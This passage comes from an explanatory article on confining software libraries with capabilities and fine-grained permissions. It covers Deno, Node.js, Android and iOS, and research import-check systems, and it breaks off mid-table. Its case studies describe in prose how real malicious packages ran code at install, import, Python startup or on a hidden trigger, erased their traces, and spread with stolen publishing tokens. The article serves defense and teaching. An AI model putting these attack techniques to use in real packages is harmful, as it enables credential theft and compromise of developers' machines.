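# Sandboxing software libraries with capabilities and fine-grained permissions

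## Why one compromised library can do whatever its program can do

Library sandboxing restricts a single library's access to files, the network, and secrets such as passwords, separately from the program that uses it. Operating systems have long limited whole programs and user accounts. Limits on the parts inside a program are much rarer, and the standard JavaScript and Python environments apply none by default.

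A library is code that one person writes and others reuse, for instance to parse dates or talk to a database. Authors publish libraries as packages in a registry, and developers install and update them from there. The main registry for JavaScript is npm; for Python it is PyPI. A library that a program uses is a dependency of that program. Dependencies usually have dependencies of their own, which are called transitive dependencies when the program's developer didn't pick them. In a supply chain attack, attackers reach their victims through software that the victims install and trust.

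Suppose a web server has three dependencies. `http-client` fetches data from other machines, so it needs network access. `logger` writes lines to files in the folder `./logs`. `colour` takes text and returns it formatted to appear green or red in a terminal, so it needs no access to anything else. An attacker then takes over the maintainer's account and publishes an update of `colour`. The new version still colours text. In an ordinary setup, it also opens the file in the developer's home directory where npm keeps the developer's publishing token, and sends the token to the attacker's server.

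### How the bad version arrives

The web server may get that update without its developer deciding to install it. A project's list of dependencies often gives a range of acceptable versions ("1.4 or later") so that bug fixes come in without anyone editing the list. The package manager, the program that downloads packages, picks the newest version in the range.

FutureSearch's *Catching the LiteLLM PyPI Attack* (2026) records such an arrival to the minute. LiteLLM is a Python library that gives programs a common interface to many AI models. On 24 March 2026, an attacker uploaded a malicious version, 1.82.8, to PyPI at 10:52 UTC. At 10:58, the code editor on a FutureSearch engineer's laptop started a small helper program that depended on LiteLLM, and the package manager fetched the malicious version in a batch of 77 packages. The engineer had not asked for LiteLLM. Version 1.82.8 had the highest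 version number so far, so it satisfied every requirement of the form "this version or later".

The engineer's main project was not affected by the attack because its dependency list required a LiteLLM version below 1.77.3. Restricting versions this way protects against a new attack, but it also blocks fixes for old security holes.

### One process, one set of rights

When a program starts, the operating system creates a process, a running instance of the program with its own memory, and ties it to a user account. Whenever code in the process tries to open a file or a network connection, the operating system checks whether the account has the right to do so. Libraries load into the same process as the program that uses them, so when the web server calls `colour`, execution jumps from one place in memory to another without involving the operating system. If `colour` then tries to open the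 token file, the request identifies the process but not the library that made it. The web server runs under the developer's account, which has permission to read the file, so the operating system lets `colour` read it too.

This access is called ambient authority. Code has it merely because of the program or user account it runs under, without anyone granting it explicitly. The opposite principle, least privilege, is that each part of a system should have only the access its task needs. The web server falls far short of this, because `logger` needs only one folder and `colour` needs no access, yet both can reach the developer's whole home directory and the open internet.

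One of the two basic ways to close the gap is to use permissions. A permission is a policy entry that lets a named subject (a program, package, function or agent) perform a kind of operation, for example "`logger` may write to `./logs`". To enforce this, some mechanism has to intercept each attempted write, work out which package is responsible, and check the policy. Identifying the package is hard because packages call each other all the time.

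A capability is an unforgeable reference that both names a resource and gives the right to use it. With capabilities, the web server would open `./logs` itself and pass `logger` an object through which it can write there. `logger` can write because it holds the object, so there is no need to identify the caller. `colour` never received such an object, so it has nothing to call. Any code can type the string `./logs`, but because a capability is unforgeable, code can get one only from other code that already has it. Capabilities restrict nothing while ambient authority remains. If `colour` can import the language's standard file module, it can open files without being passed an object by the web server.

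(Several tools use "capability" for a category of access, such as "network" or "files". By these definitions that is a permission.)

### Installation, loading and calling

Library code gets to run at three moments, and a limit that covers one of them can miss the others.

An npm package can run code before the program that uses it starts, because it can include scripts that the package manager runs during installation. Legitimate packages use these scripts to compile code or write initial settings. On 11 July 2026 an attacker published version 8.14.0 of `jscrambler`, the command-line client of a commercial service that protects JavaScript code. Socket's *jscrambler npm Package Compromised in Supply Chain Attack* (2026) reports that a new install script in this release unpacked one of three hidden programs, for Linux, Windows or macOS, and started it in the background. That program searched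 for cloud credentials, browser data, cryptocurrency wallets and the configuration files of AI coding tools. The victim did not have to import or run `jscrambler`. The malware could use any secrets available to the npm process, which on a laptop means roughly everything the developer's account can read. Limiting what the web server can do would not have helped, because the malware ran during installation and did not need the server to be running.

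A library loads when a program imports it. JavaScript and Python then run the top level of the imported file so that the library can set itself up, and any code an attacker has put there runs too. The `jscrambler` attacker switched to this method partway through the attack. Versions 8.14.0, 8.16.0 and 8.17.0 used an install script. From 8.18.0, published about two and a half hours after 8.14.0, the attacker dropped the script and put the same loader at the top of the package's main files. Socket found that the data-stealing program was byte-for-byte identical in every malicious release. The attacker had made only a small edit to change the trigger, but developers could no longer rely on npm's option to ignore install scripts.

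Three days later, another attacker relied from the start on code that runs when a package is loaded. Microsoft (2026) traced five malicious versions of packages from AsyncAPI, a project that maintains a standard for describing message-based interfaces, published within about ninety minutes. One of the packages, `@asyncapi/specs`, is a transitive dependency of many other tools, so the code ran on machines whose owners had probably never heard of it. On import, the malicious code started a hidden process that downloaded a second stage, which gave the attacker remote control of the machine. The second stage also had a module for stealing credentials, but the attacker had left it switched off.

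Schneier (2026) reports in *Python Supply-Chain Compromise* that LiteLLM 1.82.8 ran malicious code every time Python started, even if no program imported the library. Python reads files ending in `.pth` when it starts, mainly to learn where to find modules, and runs code that it finds in them. The poisoned package contained such a file. Any Python program in the same environment would therefore trigger the malicious code, including programs that didn't use LiteLLM, and a restriction that takes effect at the import statement would have come too late. The malicious code also started a new Python process, which read the same `.pth` file and started another, and so on up to about 11,000 processes, a consequence the attacker apparently overlooked. The laptop froze, which led the engineer to investigate.

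Finally, malicious code can run when the program calls one of the library's functions. `indexed-btree`, a copycat of `sorted-btree`, a library that keeps data in sorted order, had no install script. According to The Hacker News' *Malicious npm Package indexed-btree Hid Its Loader in Runtime Code Before Removal* (2026), which reports an analysis by the security company Checkmarx, the loader was inside `set()`, the function that stores an entry, so it ran during normal use of the library. The package first appeared in June 2026, and npm had removed it by 22 September. Checkmarx interprets the design as a response to npm version 12, which stopped running install scripts automatically.

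OSV's *MAL-2026-6193* (2026), an entry in a public database of vulnerabilities and malicious packages, describes `ordered-btree`, which impersonated the same library and appears to belong to the same operation. The two reports give almost the same address for the blockchain contract that held the next stage. The malicious code in `ordered-btree` ran only when a program called `set()` with the key 100, so a test that didn't use that key would show nothing wrong. Afterwards the malware deleted its files and removed its own 16-line trigger from the library, so that someone who inspected the installed package later would find harmless code.

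A library that sorts data in memory has no reason to start another program, but `ordered-btree` did so as its first step, as did the AsyncAPI packages, `jscrambler` and LiteLLM. The malicious step was often one that the library's real task never required, so enforcing least privilege could have stopped the attack there. The right to start a process is powerful because a child process may run outside the limits the language placed on its parent.

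### How far one package reaches

The publishing token that `colour` tries to steal is a realistic target because attackers can use it to spread from one compromised package to many others. *ChainDrop Worm Hits 400 npm Packages with Two Billion Monthly Installs* (Muncaster, 2026) reports that on 4 August 2026 attackers took over the GitHub account of a maintainer of `keyv`, a storage library with about 127 million weekly downloads. From there, a self-spreading program called ChainDrop reached more than 430 packages.

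Microsoft's analysis of ChainDrop describes how the worm spreads. An install script starts the worm, which searches the machine for credentials, including npm tokens. If it finds a usable token, it lists every package that the token's owner can publish. It downloads the latest release of each, adds itself and an install script, raises the last part of the version number by one, and publishes the result. Maintainers raise that part of the number for routine bug fixes, so any project that automatically accepts bug fixes also accepts the worm.

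The affected packages had two billion monthly installs between them. This is the packages' normal traffic, and the number of infected machines is surely far lower. The `jscrambler` case gives an idea of the difference. The package had about 15,800 downloads a week, but Fortuna (2026), in *Security Incident Postmortem*, the company's own account, puts downloads of all the malicious versions at 1,614. He suspects that most of those came from security researchers, since a typical Saturday brought only about 391. (The count does include four helper packages that pointed to the poisoned 8.18.0, which the company identified two days after the attack. Transitive dependencies are easy to miss even for the people who publish them.)

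The broadest evidence for 2026 comes from researchers at Databricks, a data and AI company, who examined about 5,400 malicious npm packages published between December 2025 and October 2026. EconoTimes' *Compromised npm packages account for most exposure in study* (2026) reports that legitimate packages that attackers had compromised made up 7% of the sample but more than 99% of the recorded download exposure. Attackers had created the other 93% themselves, and few people downloaded those. Even `indexed-btree`, with its reported millions of downloads, has far fewer than `keyv`.

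The researchers took download figures as monthly snapshots when they scanned each package, so "exposure" again measures popularity more than harm. The sample is also incomplete, because 7% of 5,400 is about 380 packages, fewer than Microsoft counted in ChainDrop alone. But the gap between 7% and 99% is so wide that neither problem is likely to overturn the conclusion that most of the danger comes from libraries that deserved their users' trust until they were attacked.

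This weakens the usual advice to choose dependencies carefully. In most of the compromises that Databricks studied, the attacker published through a legitimate account and the ownership records stayed the same. The AsyncAPI packages even carried valid provenance attestations, which are signed statements of the source code and build process a package came from. The statements were accurate because the attacker had got into the project's own build process. Such compromises also happen outside npm. Google Cloud attributes a series of them on PyPI, npm and Docker Hub (a registry of ready-made software environments) between February and May 2026 to a single group, TeamPCP, which typically planted programs that steal credentials.

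Blocking install scripts would prevent many of these attacks, at least for now. EconoTimes reports that attackers added or changed such scripts in 78% of the compromised versions. But the `jscrambler` attacker took only an afternoon to switch to a method that didn't use them.

A limit on `colour` itself would hold no matter who published the update or when its code ran, provided that something enforces the limit at all three moments. Such a limit would do less against a compromised `http-client`, which needs the network for its ordinary work. Permission to use the network would also let the attacker send data out, so the policy would have to restrict which machines the library may contact or deny it access to the token.

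### Agents in the same position

An agent is an AI model that carries out tasks by calling tools, running commands and editing files. It commonly runs under the account of the developer who started it, so, like `colour`, it has access to the token file even when its task has nothing to do with publishing. Attackers can turn an agent against its user by planting instructions in text that it reads. An agent can also do damage by mistake.

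The LiteLLM incident included a harmless mistake of that kind. When the FutureSearch engineer asked Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, about the thousands of processes, it said that the encoded commands were not malware and that the cause was a runaway loop in its own tools. It identified the poisoned package at 11:40, almost half an hour into the investigation. By then it had been running commands and reading logs all over the laptop. That access was useful here, but most coding tasks need less. The helper program that had fetched LiteLLM was a tool server, which gives AI models access to tools. FutureSearch notes that the malicious package was triggered again when the engineer later reopened the editor.

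## What Deno and mobile systems limit today

Deno is a runtime for JavaScript and TypeScript that competes with Node.js, the runtime that most npm packages target. Unlike Node.js, Deno blocks most access by default. Code can't read files, use the network, start other programs or read environment variables (settings that a program receives at startup, often including passwords) unless the user allows it. Android and iOS restrict apps in a similar way. All three give permissions to a whole program, so a library gets every permission that the program loading it has.

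### From a call to a decision

JavaScript has no commands for opening a file or a network connection, so code has to call functions that the runtime provides. In Deno, these functions sit in a Rust layer around the JavaScript engine. AlHamdan and Staicu write in *Welcome to Jurassic Park*, a 2025 study of Deno's security, that this layer is meant to intercept every operation that reaches outside the program.

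Suppose the developer of the web server from the previous section starts it with this command:

```
deno run --allow-net=localhost:8000,api.example.com --allow-write=./logs main.ts
```

The server may now accept connections on port 8000, contact one outside machine and write to one folder. When `http-client` requests a page, Deno checks the operation and its target against the deny and allow rules. A matching deny rule blocks the call even if an allow rule also matches. If only an allow rule matches, Deno passes the request to the operating system, which still checks the user account's permissions.

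If no rule matches and the program is running in a terminal, Deno pauses it and asks the user, who can allow the operation, refuse it, or allow everything of that kind. The call instead fails with a `NotCapable` error on a server whose output goes to a log file, or if the developer has passed `--no-prompt`.

A program can catch this error like any other. An honest program can then print a helpful message, but a malicious `colour` can fail silently and go on colouring text. It can even avoid the failed attempt, because according to Deno's *Security and permissions*, any code in the program can call `Deno.permissions.query` to check whether a permission is in place.

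Deno's `NotCapable` error also breaks some harmless packages. Deno gives the example of a dependency that tries to read 20 environment variables and works if they are missing, but can't handle the error. Version 2.6 therefore added `--ignore-env` and `--ignore-read`, which make the selected variables look unset and the selected files look absent.

Most Deno permission flags accept a scope. `--allow-read=./data` covers that folder and everything below it, and `--allow-env="AWS_*"` covers all variables whose names start with `AWS_`. Network rules name a host and optionally a port, and they cover subdomains only if the developer adds a wildcard. A flag without a scope allows the whole category, and `-A` turns the sandbox off.

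`--allow-run` and `--allow-ffi` each grant nearly as much access as `-A`. `--allow-run` lets a script start other programs, which don't inherit Deno's limits, so a script that may start `deno` can start a second copy with `-A`. `--allow-ffi` lets a script load compiled machine code, which can call the operating system directly, bypassing the Rust layer. Scoping `--allow-run` to one trusted program helps, unless the script can also write to the folder where that program is stored and replace it with another. On Linux and macOS, certain environment variables make any program load extra code as it starts. Deno lets a script set these for a child process only if the run permission is unscoped.

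Deno has separate protection for the installation step, which the `jscrambler` attacker used first. It doesn't run npm packages' install scripts by default, but a developer can approve them package by package. Deno 2.9 also refuses npm releases less than 24 hours old by default, which keeps out a poisoned `colour` only if someone detects it within a day. However, `dx`, a shortcut for running a package's command-line program, grants every permission unless the user passes a permission flag, and it runs install scripts once the user has agreed to the download.

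### Storing and giving up permissions

Long lists of flags are a nuisance to type, which tempts people to use short, broad ones. Deno introduced permission sets in version 2.5 to make this easier. A project stores them under names of its choice in its configuration file, `deno.json`:

```json
{
  "permissions": {
    "server": {
      "net": ["localhost:8000", "api.example.com"],
      "write": ["./logs"]
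    }
  }
}
```

The developer then runs `deno run -P=server main.ts`. Tests, benchmarks and programs that Deno compiles into a single file can have their own sets. In a study published a few months earlier, AlHamdan and Staicu criticised Deno for having no permissions file. They also wanted such a file to specify permissions for each module (a file of code that other files can import), which the sets don't do. The `server` set applies to a run of the whole program, so the developer can't use it to give `logger` access to the folder and `colour` no access at all.

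A program can also give up permissions while it runs. For example, it can read its settings at startup and then call `Deno.permissions.revoke` to drop read access. Deno recommends this as a simple way to limit what the remaining code, including dependencies, can do. Revoking a permission returns it to the state where Deno would prompt the user, so someone at a terminal could still grant it again.

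Revoking a permission comes too late if `colour` has its malicious code at the top level, as the later `jscrambler` releases did, because that code finishes running before the first line of the server's main file. A developer can get around this by loading `colour` with a dynamic import after revoking the permission, but every other package on the thread loses that permission too.

### One privilege level per thread

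A thread is a sequence of instructions that can run in parallel with others in the same process. A program and its packages normally share one thread, and according to Deno's documentation, it is "not possible for different modules to have different privilege levels" within a thread.

The command above blocks the token theft from the previous section at two steps. `colour` can't read the file in the home directory, because the server has no read permission, and it can't contact the attacker's server. A tight policy for the whole program therefore gives substantial protection, even though it contains no rule about `colour`.

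But `colour` still has every permission the server needs for its other packages. It can delete or falsify the logs, and it can send data to `api.example.com`. If the server also needs `--allow-read=./config` to read a folder with the database password, `colour` can read the password too. If the developer gets tired of listing hosts and shortens the network flag to `--allow-net`, `colour` can send the password anywhere. Each new package that needs access adds to what all the others can do, so the policy protects least in large programs, which have the most dependencies.

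Packages can also reach some data without any permission, because those on the same thread share the JavaScript environment. AlHamdan and Staicu found no built-in mechanism in Deno that limits how an untrusted dependency affects trusted code. They also tested prototype pollution, an attack that alters the shared template from which other objects take their default behaviour. Deno blocks one way of carrying out this attack but leaves a harder one open.

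Deno users also ask about per-package limits. In *Why Are Permissions Enabled Globally and Not Per Dependency?*, a post on Deno's help site, a newcomer asks how to give file access to just one package. Their small project already needs three permissions, and they are tempted to use `-A` instead.

### Workers and the permission broker

Deno's documentation recommends moving untrusted code to a worker, a separate thread that exchanges messages with the main one. The program that creates the worker can pass it a list of permissions, for example two files to read and one host to contact, or `"none"`. A worker can't have more access than its parent, but if the developer forgets to set its permissions, it inherits all of the parent's.

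To confine `colour`, the developer would write a small worker file that imports it, start that worker with permissions set to `"none"`, and make sure that no other part of the program imports `colour` directly. This would stop the attack both when `colour` loads and when the server later calls it. But every place in the server that uses `colour` would have to send the text to the worker as a message and wait for the coloured version, instead of simply calling a function. Few developers would do this for a formatting function that the server calls on every log line. A component that parses uploaded files is a better candidate, since the server calls it less often and each call does more work. Deno still marks worker permissions as unstable, so their interface may change.

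Deno can also hand permission decisions to a permission broker, an external process that the developer supplies. While the broker is active, Deno ignores all permission flags and shows no prompts. For each check, it sends the broker the kind of permission, a request number, a timestamp, the Deno process ID and usually the path or host in question. The broker answers "allow" or "deny", optionally with a reason. If the connection breaks or an answer doesn't match its request, Deno terminates the program immediately. Deno introduced the broker as an experimental feature in version 2.6, mainly for companies that run other people's code and want to decide centrally what that code may do.

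The broker could apply rules that flags can't express, such as allowing writes only during certain hours. It couldn't apply a different rule to `colour` than to `logger`, because the message doesn't include the name of the package that made the call. Deno can find this out by recording the chain of function calls behind each request, which it does when `DENO_TRACE_PERMISSIONS` is set. This tracing is off by default because it slows programs down. The trace goes to the user or the audit log and doesn't affect the decision, although a prototype of per-module permissions tries to use the call stack to decide whether to allow a request.

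### The permission model in Node.js

Node.js has also had permissions since version 20.0.0, and has treated them as stable since versions 22.13.0 and 23.5.0. They are off unless the developer passes `--permission`, which restricts file access, network connections, child processes, native code and several other features. As in Deno, a configuration file can hold the grants, and a program can drop them while it runs. Dropping a grant in Node.js is irreversible, but files and connections already open stay open.

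The grants apply to the whole process, and Node.js promises less than Deno does. Node.js' *Permissions* compares the model to a seat belt that keeps trusted code from causing damage by accident, and warns that malicious code can bypass it. One documented gap is that a restricted process can send a signal that forces another Node.js process of the same user to open its debugging interface. The maintainers consider it the operating system's responsibility to control such signals. So for `colour`, the model might catch a careless mistake, but it doesn't guarantee protection against the attacker's update.

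Node.js also once had a module-based mechanism, called policies. The documentation for version 20 already marked it as deprecated, and the current permissions page no longer includes it.

### Where Deno's checks have failed

Deno has advertised that developers can run untrusted code with confidence and no longer need to audit their dependencies. AlHamdan and Staicu tested both claims and concluded that each was partly broken. Most of their attacks start from permissions a user might reasonably grant and don't require breaking the JavaScript engine.

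In the first group of problems, one permission silently includes others. Linux makes a process's environment variables and the machine's memory size available as special files, so a program with unscoped read permission could read them without the permissions meant for environment variables and system information. Unscoped write permission was worse because it let a program change the scripts that a user's terminal runs at startup, or replace the browser, and the attacker's code would later run outside Deno. Deno had warned that running programs and loading native code could break the sandbox, but reading and writing files looked harmless by comparison.

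Deno has partly fixed this. *CVE-2024-34346 Detail*, in the US government's National Vulnerability Database, records that since version 1.43 programs need `--allow-all` to open files in several sensitive system folders. The rule for one of them, `/etc`, seems to have changed again, because the current reference shows how to read it with an ordinary flag. A user's own startup scripts are normally in the home directory, which isn't on the list. Unscoped write permission therefore still amounts to full access and is unsafe to give to a program with untrusted dependencies.

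The second problem involved imports. Deno can load code from a web address, and it fetches the files named in ordinary import statements before the program starts. At the time, it did this without checking the network permission. An address can carry data, so a package could use an import to notify an attacker each time someone ran the program. A more elaborate version worked on programs that could read and write files but had no network permission. On the first run, the malicious code read a secret and added an import statement to one of the program's own files, with the secret in the address. On the second run, Deno fetched that address, which sent the secret to the attacker.

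OSV's *Deno vulnerable to Exposure of Sensitive Information to an Unauthorized Actor* (2025) lists this as fixed in Deno 2.0.0, which introduced a separate import permission. By default, Deno now loads web code only from seven hosts, and only over encrypted connections. Imports from these hosts still don't require network permission. Deno's developers justify this by saying that the hosts are trusted public registries, which they don't expect to leak data through addresses, presumably because an attacker who publishes a file there can't see who requests it.

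The third problem is symbolic links, small files that redirect to another file or folder. Suppose a user downloads a project that requests access only to its own `cache` folder. If that folder contains a link to the root of the disk, the program could use it to reach any file the user's account can open, because Deno checked the link's location but not its target. A company that handles vulnerability reports rated this high severity.

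Deno still describes following existing links out of permitted folders as normal behaviour. To limit the damage, it requires additional permission for links into certain system folders, and unscoped read and write access to create a link through Deno. With permission to write only to `./logs`, `colour` therefore can't create a link out of the folder, but it can use an existing one. Node.js also follows links out of permitted folders, and tells developers to make sure that those folders contain no relative links.

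The fixes took some persistence. AlHamdan and Staicu reported the first two groups of problems in early 2023 and had a friendly exchange with Deno's team, but the team then stopped answering. At the end of that year, the researchers went to the vulnerability company and added the problems with symbolic links to their report. Deno's team then became more cooperative and promised the restriction on imports.

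A permission rule identifies a resource by name, such as a path or a host, but a name can lead to a resource the rule wasn't meant to cover, and one resource can have several names. Attackers can exploit this with links. AlHamdan and Staicu mention that attackers can also get permission for a domain they own and then point it at machines inside the user's private network. Deno has had similar bugs more recently. OSV's *Deno* (2026) reports that before version 2.8.1, `fetch()` checked the host name against the network deny rules but didn't check the IP addresses it resolved to. According to OSV's *Deno Permission Bypass via Unicode Normalization Mismatch on macOS (APFS)* (2026), deny rules for paths on macOS failed before version 2.7.14 because the system accepts different encodings of the same file name. Deny rules are especially fragile because they must cover every possible name for the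 forbidden resource, whereas an allow rule rejects any name it doesn't recognise.

`colour` could have exploited another 2026 bug directly. An npm package's `package.json` file names the file that holds its main code. Lutra Security's *BYONM module resolution allows `package.json` main path traversal to bypass `--allow-read` restrictions* (2026) describes how, when developers managed the package folder themselves, a malicious package could name a file elsewhere on the disk, and Deno would read it without checking the read permission. Deno 2.7.12 fixed this.

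### Phones isolate apps from each other

Deno's checks run inside the process they are supposed to limit. On phones, the operating system enforces most limits from outside the app's process. Android gives each app its own user account at installation, along with a private folder that other apps can't open. Two apps on one phone are about as separate as two people's accounts on a shared computer. iOS similarly confines each app to its own container of files.

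An Android developer lists the permissions an app may need in its manifest, a file inside the app, and the app can't get any others. Android grants low-risk permissions at installation. Since Android 6, it has asked the user about sensitive ones, such as location, contacts and the camera, while the app is running. iOS asks when the app first tries to use the data and shows the developer's explanation. Users can withdraw these permissions later in the settings.

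This arrangement gives phones a second layer of protection that Deno lacks. AlHamdan and Staicu point out that Android's additional access controls keep apps from changing sensitive system files, so permission to write files doesn't give an app control of the device.

Within a mobile app, as in Deno, libraries share the app's permissions. Mobile developers often call libraries SDKs (software development kits), especially when a company supplies them for advertising, analytics or payments. If a weather app has permission to use the phone's location, its advertising SDK can use the location too. The permission prompt names the weather app, and the user can't allow location access for the forecast while denying it for advertising. The SDK can usually send the data out as well, because Android grants internet access at installation.

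Researchers have tried modifying Android to distinguish between the components of an app. In 2014, Wang and colleagues published Compac, a modified version of Android 4.0.4 that identified a component by the names of the running Java packages and gave it only some of the app's permissions. Compac was only slightly slower than the original, scoring about 97% as high in a general performance benchmark.

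FlexDroid, published by Seo and colleagues in 2016, dealt with harder cases. Developers stated in the manifest what each library could access and what should happen if it tried to access more, such as giving it made-up data. When an app requests the location, the request goes to a system service in another process, which can normally identify only the app, not the library. FlexDroid therefore also examined the chain of function calls inside the app, and it isolated native code that could otherwise have tampered with that chain. Both systems remained research prototypes. They require changes to Android that Google didn't adopt, so app developers can't use them on ordinary phones.

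Google then built its own solution, the SDK Runtime, as part of its Privacy Sandbox project. It moved participating SDKs, mainly for advertising, into a separate process with its own storage and a small, fixed set of permissions. This is a much stronger boundary than a check on package names, because the SDK can't read the app's memory. But SDK companies had to rewrite their products, for instance so that one process could draw an advertisement inside another's window. Many of these companies also profit from the access the runtime would have taken away. In October 2025, Google announced that it was retiring the SDK Runtime and most of the Privacy Sandbox, citing low adoption.

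Apple chose disclosure, which is less demanding for SDK companies. Since 2024, it has been phasing in an App Store requirement for privacy manifests, which are files where an SDK's makers declare what data it collects, for what purposes, and why it calls certain functions that could help identify a device. Apple's development tools combine these files into a report for the app developer. For widely used SDKs, Apple also requires a signature, which helps developers notice if a new version comes from someone else. Privacy manifests are still in use in 2026.

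Apple's privacy manifests restrict very little while the app is running. If the user has refused tracking, iOS blocks connections to web addresses that a manifest lists as used for tracking, but this doesn't affect undeclared addresses. An attacker who took over `colour` could leave its manifest unchanged, with no data collection declared, and the new code would still run with all the app's permissions.

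## Limiting a package by what it may import

Deno applies one policy to everything on a thread, so it can't treat `colour` differently from `logger`. A runtime can treat them differently if it checks earlier, when a package imports the module that performs the operation. Node.js keeps most sensitive operations in a few built-in modules, such as `fs` for files, `http` and `https` for web requests, and `child_process` for starting other programs. A runtime that controls imports can therefore let `logger` import `fs` and stop `colour` from importing it.

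Checking imports also makes it easy to identify the responsible package. In CommonJS, the older of JavaScript's two module formats, code imports a module by calling a function named `require`, and Node.js passes each file its own copy of that function. The runtime can build the package's name and a permission check into the copy:

```js
function requireFor(importer) {
  return function (target) {
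    if (!mayImport(importer, target)) {
      throw new Error(`${importer} may not import ${target}`);
    }
    return require(target);
  };
}
```

When Node.js loads `colour`, it would pass in `requireFor("colour")`. The legitimate version imports nothing sensitive, so its policy can be empty. The attacker's update needs `fs` to read the publishing token and `https` to send it, but importing `fs` fails. The import fails whether it is at the top level of the file or inside a function that the server calls a week later, because both use the same `require`. If the malicious code catches the error, it still can't access the token.

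Node.js once had a similar feature, called policies, in which a file could list what each module could import. According to Node.js' documentation, the list affected only names passed to `require()` and `import`, so code could still reach modules through `require.cache`, a table of everything the program had already loaded. A Node.js maintainer, mcollina (2024), proposed deleting the feature in *Remove --experimental-policy*. Nobody was maintaining it, and people kept reporting bypasses that fell outside Node.js' threat model, in which all loaded code is trusted. Another project member commented that "a misunderstood security feature can be a vulnerability in itself". The maintainers removed policies a few weeks later. To stop `colour`, an import check has to block other ways of reaching modules and treat loaded packages as possible attackers.

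### Four permissions for npm packages

*Containing Malicious Package Updates in npm with a Lightweight Permission System* (Ferreira, Jia and colleagues, 2021) proposes an import check for Node.js with four permissions. `network`, `filesystem` and `process` each let a package import the corresponding built-in modules. `all` includes the other three and also allows language features that could bypass the checks, such as `eval`, which runs text as code.

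Package A may import package B only if A has every permission that B has, or P(B) ⊆ P(A). Without this rule, `colour` could import `http-client` and use it to send data. The rule blocks this import because `http-client` has the `network` permission and `colour` doesn't. The drawback is that every package that imports `http-client` needs `network` too, even if it never accesses the network directly.

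The check in `require` isn't enough, because JavaScript objects contain links to other objects. For example, `module.parent` leads to the module that imported the current one, and from there to a `require` function that may have more permissions. Ferreira and colleagues therefore block a list of such properties for packages without `all`. Code can also build a property's name at runtime, as in `o["par" + "ent"]`, so searching the source code would miss some uses. To catch these, their system rewrites each file as it loads. It leaves a property access alone if the name is visible in the source and harmless, and otherwise inserts a check that runs before the access.

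To see how many packages this could protect, Ferreira and colleagues estimated the permissions needed by 604,159 npm packages from February 2018. They found that 31.9% needed no permissions, 9.4% needed some, and 58.7% needed `all`. The system can't contain an attack on a package in the last group. More than half of that group (36.8% of all packages) needed `all` only because of their dependencies. Of those that needed it directly, about 5% used `eval`, and the rest changed the prototypes of built-in objects, the shared templates mentioned in the previous section. `colour` would need `all` just to let developers write `"text".green`, because it would have to add `green` to the prototype of all strings.

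The estimate is probably somewhat pessimistic, because the researchers checked 30 random packages by hand and found seven to which their analysis had assigned `all` unnecessarily. But popular packages did worse than average on some measures. For example, only 14% of the 100 packages with the most stars on GitHub needed no permissions.

The researchers also replayed three real attacks, on `eslint-scope`, `event-stream` and `electron-native-notify`. None of the affected packages had needed permissions before the attack, and the system blocked all three. The malicious code in `eslint-scope` ran from an install script, which the system could block because the script was a JavaScript file that the modified Node.js executed. An install script can also be a shell command or a compiled program, which an import check wouldn't affect.

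Across 20 command-line programs, the slowdown averaged 0.2%, with a maximum of 1.3%. All the programs worked without code changes if the permissions were set correctly.

### The alternatives they rejected

Ferreira and colleagues considered two more precise designs. Taint tracking labels sensitive data, such as the contents of the token file, and follows it through the program. It could let `http-client` use the network but stop it from sending the token, which no import rule can do. But these flows are very hard to predict from JavaScript source code, and tracking them at runtime often makes the program 40 to 100 times slower.

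A membrane wraps every object and function that passes between packages in a proxy, a stand-in that checks each use. It would detect `colour` calling a dangerous function it had received as an argument, even if `colour` imported nothing. In earlier systems, isolating a single package reportedly caused a slowdown of about 20%, and the researchers measured similar or slightly higher slowdowns with membranes between all packages.

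Callbacks also caused trouble for membranes. A package that reads a file typically gives `fs` a function to call when the data is ready, so that call crosses the boundary in the opposite direction. Under a simple rule, both sides would then need the same permissions. Exceptions could avoid this, but they would let through most of the passed references that a membrane could otherwise catch. Proxies also break code that checks whether two references point to the same object. The researchers had to adapt many existing packages to run their prototype.

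These seem like good reasons for a system meant for all of npm. A company protecting one important program might accept a 20% slowdown, but it would still have to fix the packages that proxies break.

### Permissions on a module's contents

The `filesystem` permission would give `logger` every function in `fs`, although it only needs to add lines to a file. Vasilakis, Staicu and colleagues (2021), in *Preventing Dynamic Library Compromise on Node.js via RWX-Based Privilege Reduction*, set permissions on individual functions and values instead. In their system, Mir, a package can have permission to read a value (R), overwrite it (W), execute it (X) or import a module (I). A policy for `logger` might look like this:

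```
logger:
  require: RX
  require("fs"): I
  require("fs").appendFile: RX
```

With this policy, `logger` can append to files but can't call `fs.readFile` to read the token. Mir enforces the policy by enclosing the package's code in a function where names such as `require`, `eval` and `process` refer to wrapped versions. Each wrapper checks the permission before allowing the access.

Mir doesn't check the arguments of a permitted call, so `logger` could still append to any file the user can change. Appending to a file can be enough for an attack. A malicious version of the package `leetlog` used `appendFile` to add the attacker's key to the list of keys that can be used to log in to the machine.

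Few developers would write such detailed policies by hand, so Mir infers them. It goes through each function in the source code and tracks which variables refer to outside functions and values. Mir adds W if the code assigns to one, X if it calls one, and R if it only mentions one. This misses names that the code computes, so Mir also loads the package once and records what it accesses. In the test suites of 81 packages, the source analysis alone covered 71% of the places where code accessed something outside the package. Adding the loading step raised this to 99%, though eight packages still had at least one access that Mir wrongly blocked.

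The loading step would run the malicious code in the attacker's version of `colour`, and the inferred policy would permit whatever that code does. Vasilakis and colleagues want to protect honest packages with security holes, and they explicitly exclude malicious ones. For example, a package might convert text into objects by passing it to `eval`, which lets attackers send it code. Mir stopped 61 of 63 exploits of such holes and slowed programs by 1.93% on average. On the other two packages, Mir crashed even without an attack.

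*You Can Run But You Can't Hide* (Ohm, Pohl and Boes, 2023) adapts policy inference to malicious updates. It infers a policy from the source code of a package's last trusted version, without running the package, and enforces that policy on the new version. If the update imports a module that its predecessor didn't use, it gets a dummy object whose functions do nothing. This blocked nine of ten past attacks, although in five of the nine the program crashed because the code couldn't handle the dummy objects. The researchers couldn't trigger the tenth attack, so they didn't count it as blocked.

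Limiting individual functions instead of whole modules didn't stop any more of these attacks, since the legitimate versions hadn't used the relevant modules at all. The main problem was false alarms. Among the 1,000 most depended-upon npm packages, 14.7% of patch updates, which normally contain only bug fixes, used a module or global object that the previous version hadn't. Ohm and colleagues considered this too many updates to block automatically.

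### NodeShield

NodeShield, which Cornelissen and Balliu (2025), in *NodeShield*, presented, is the most complete of these systems. It covers both CommonJS and the newer ES modules, which the systems by Ferreira's and Ohm's groups don't support, and it runs on an unmodified Node.js. It has seven permissions:

| Permission | What it allows |
|---|---|
| `file-system` | Reading and changing files |
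| `network` | Network connections, including the global function `fetch` |
| `command` | Starting other programs and worker threads |
| `addon` | Loading native code |
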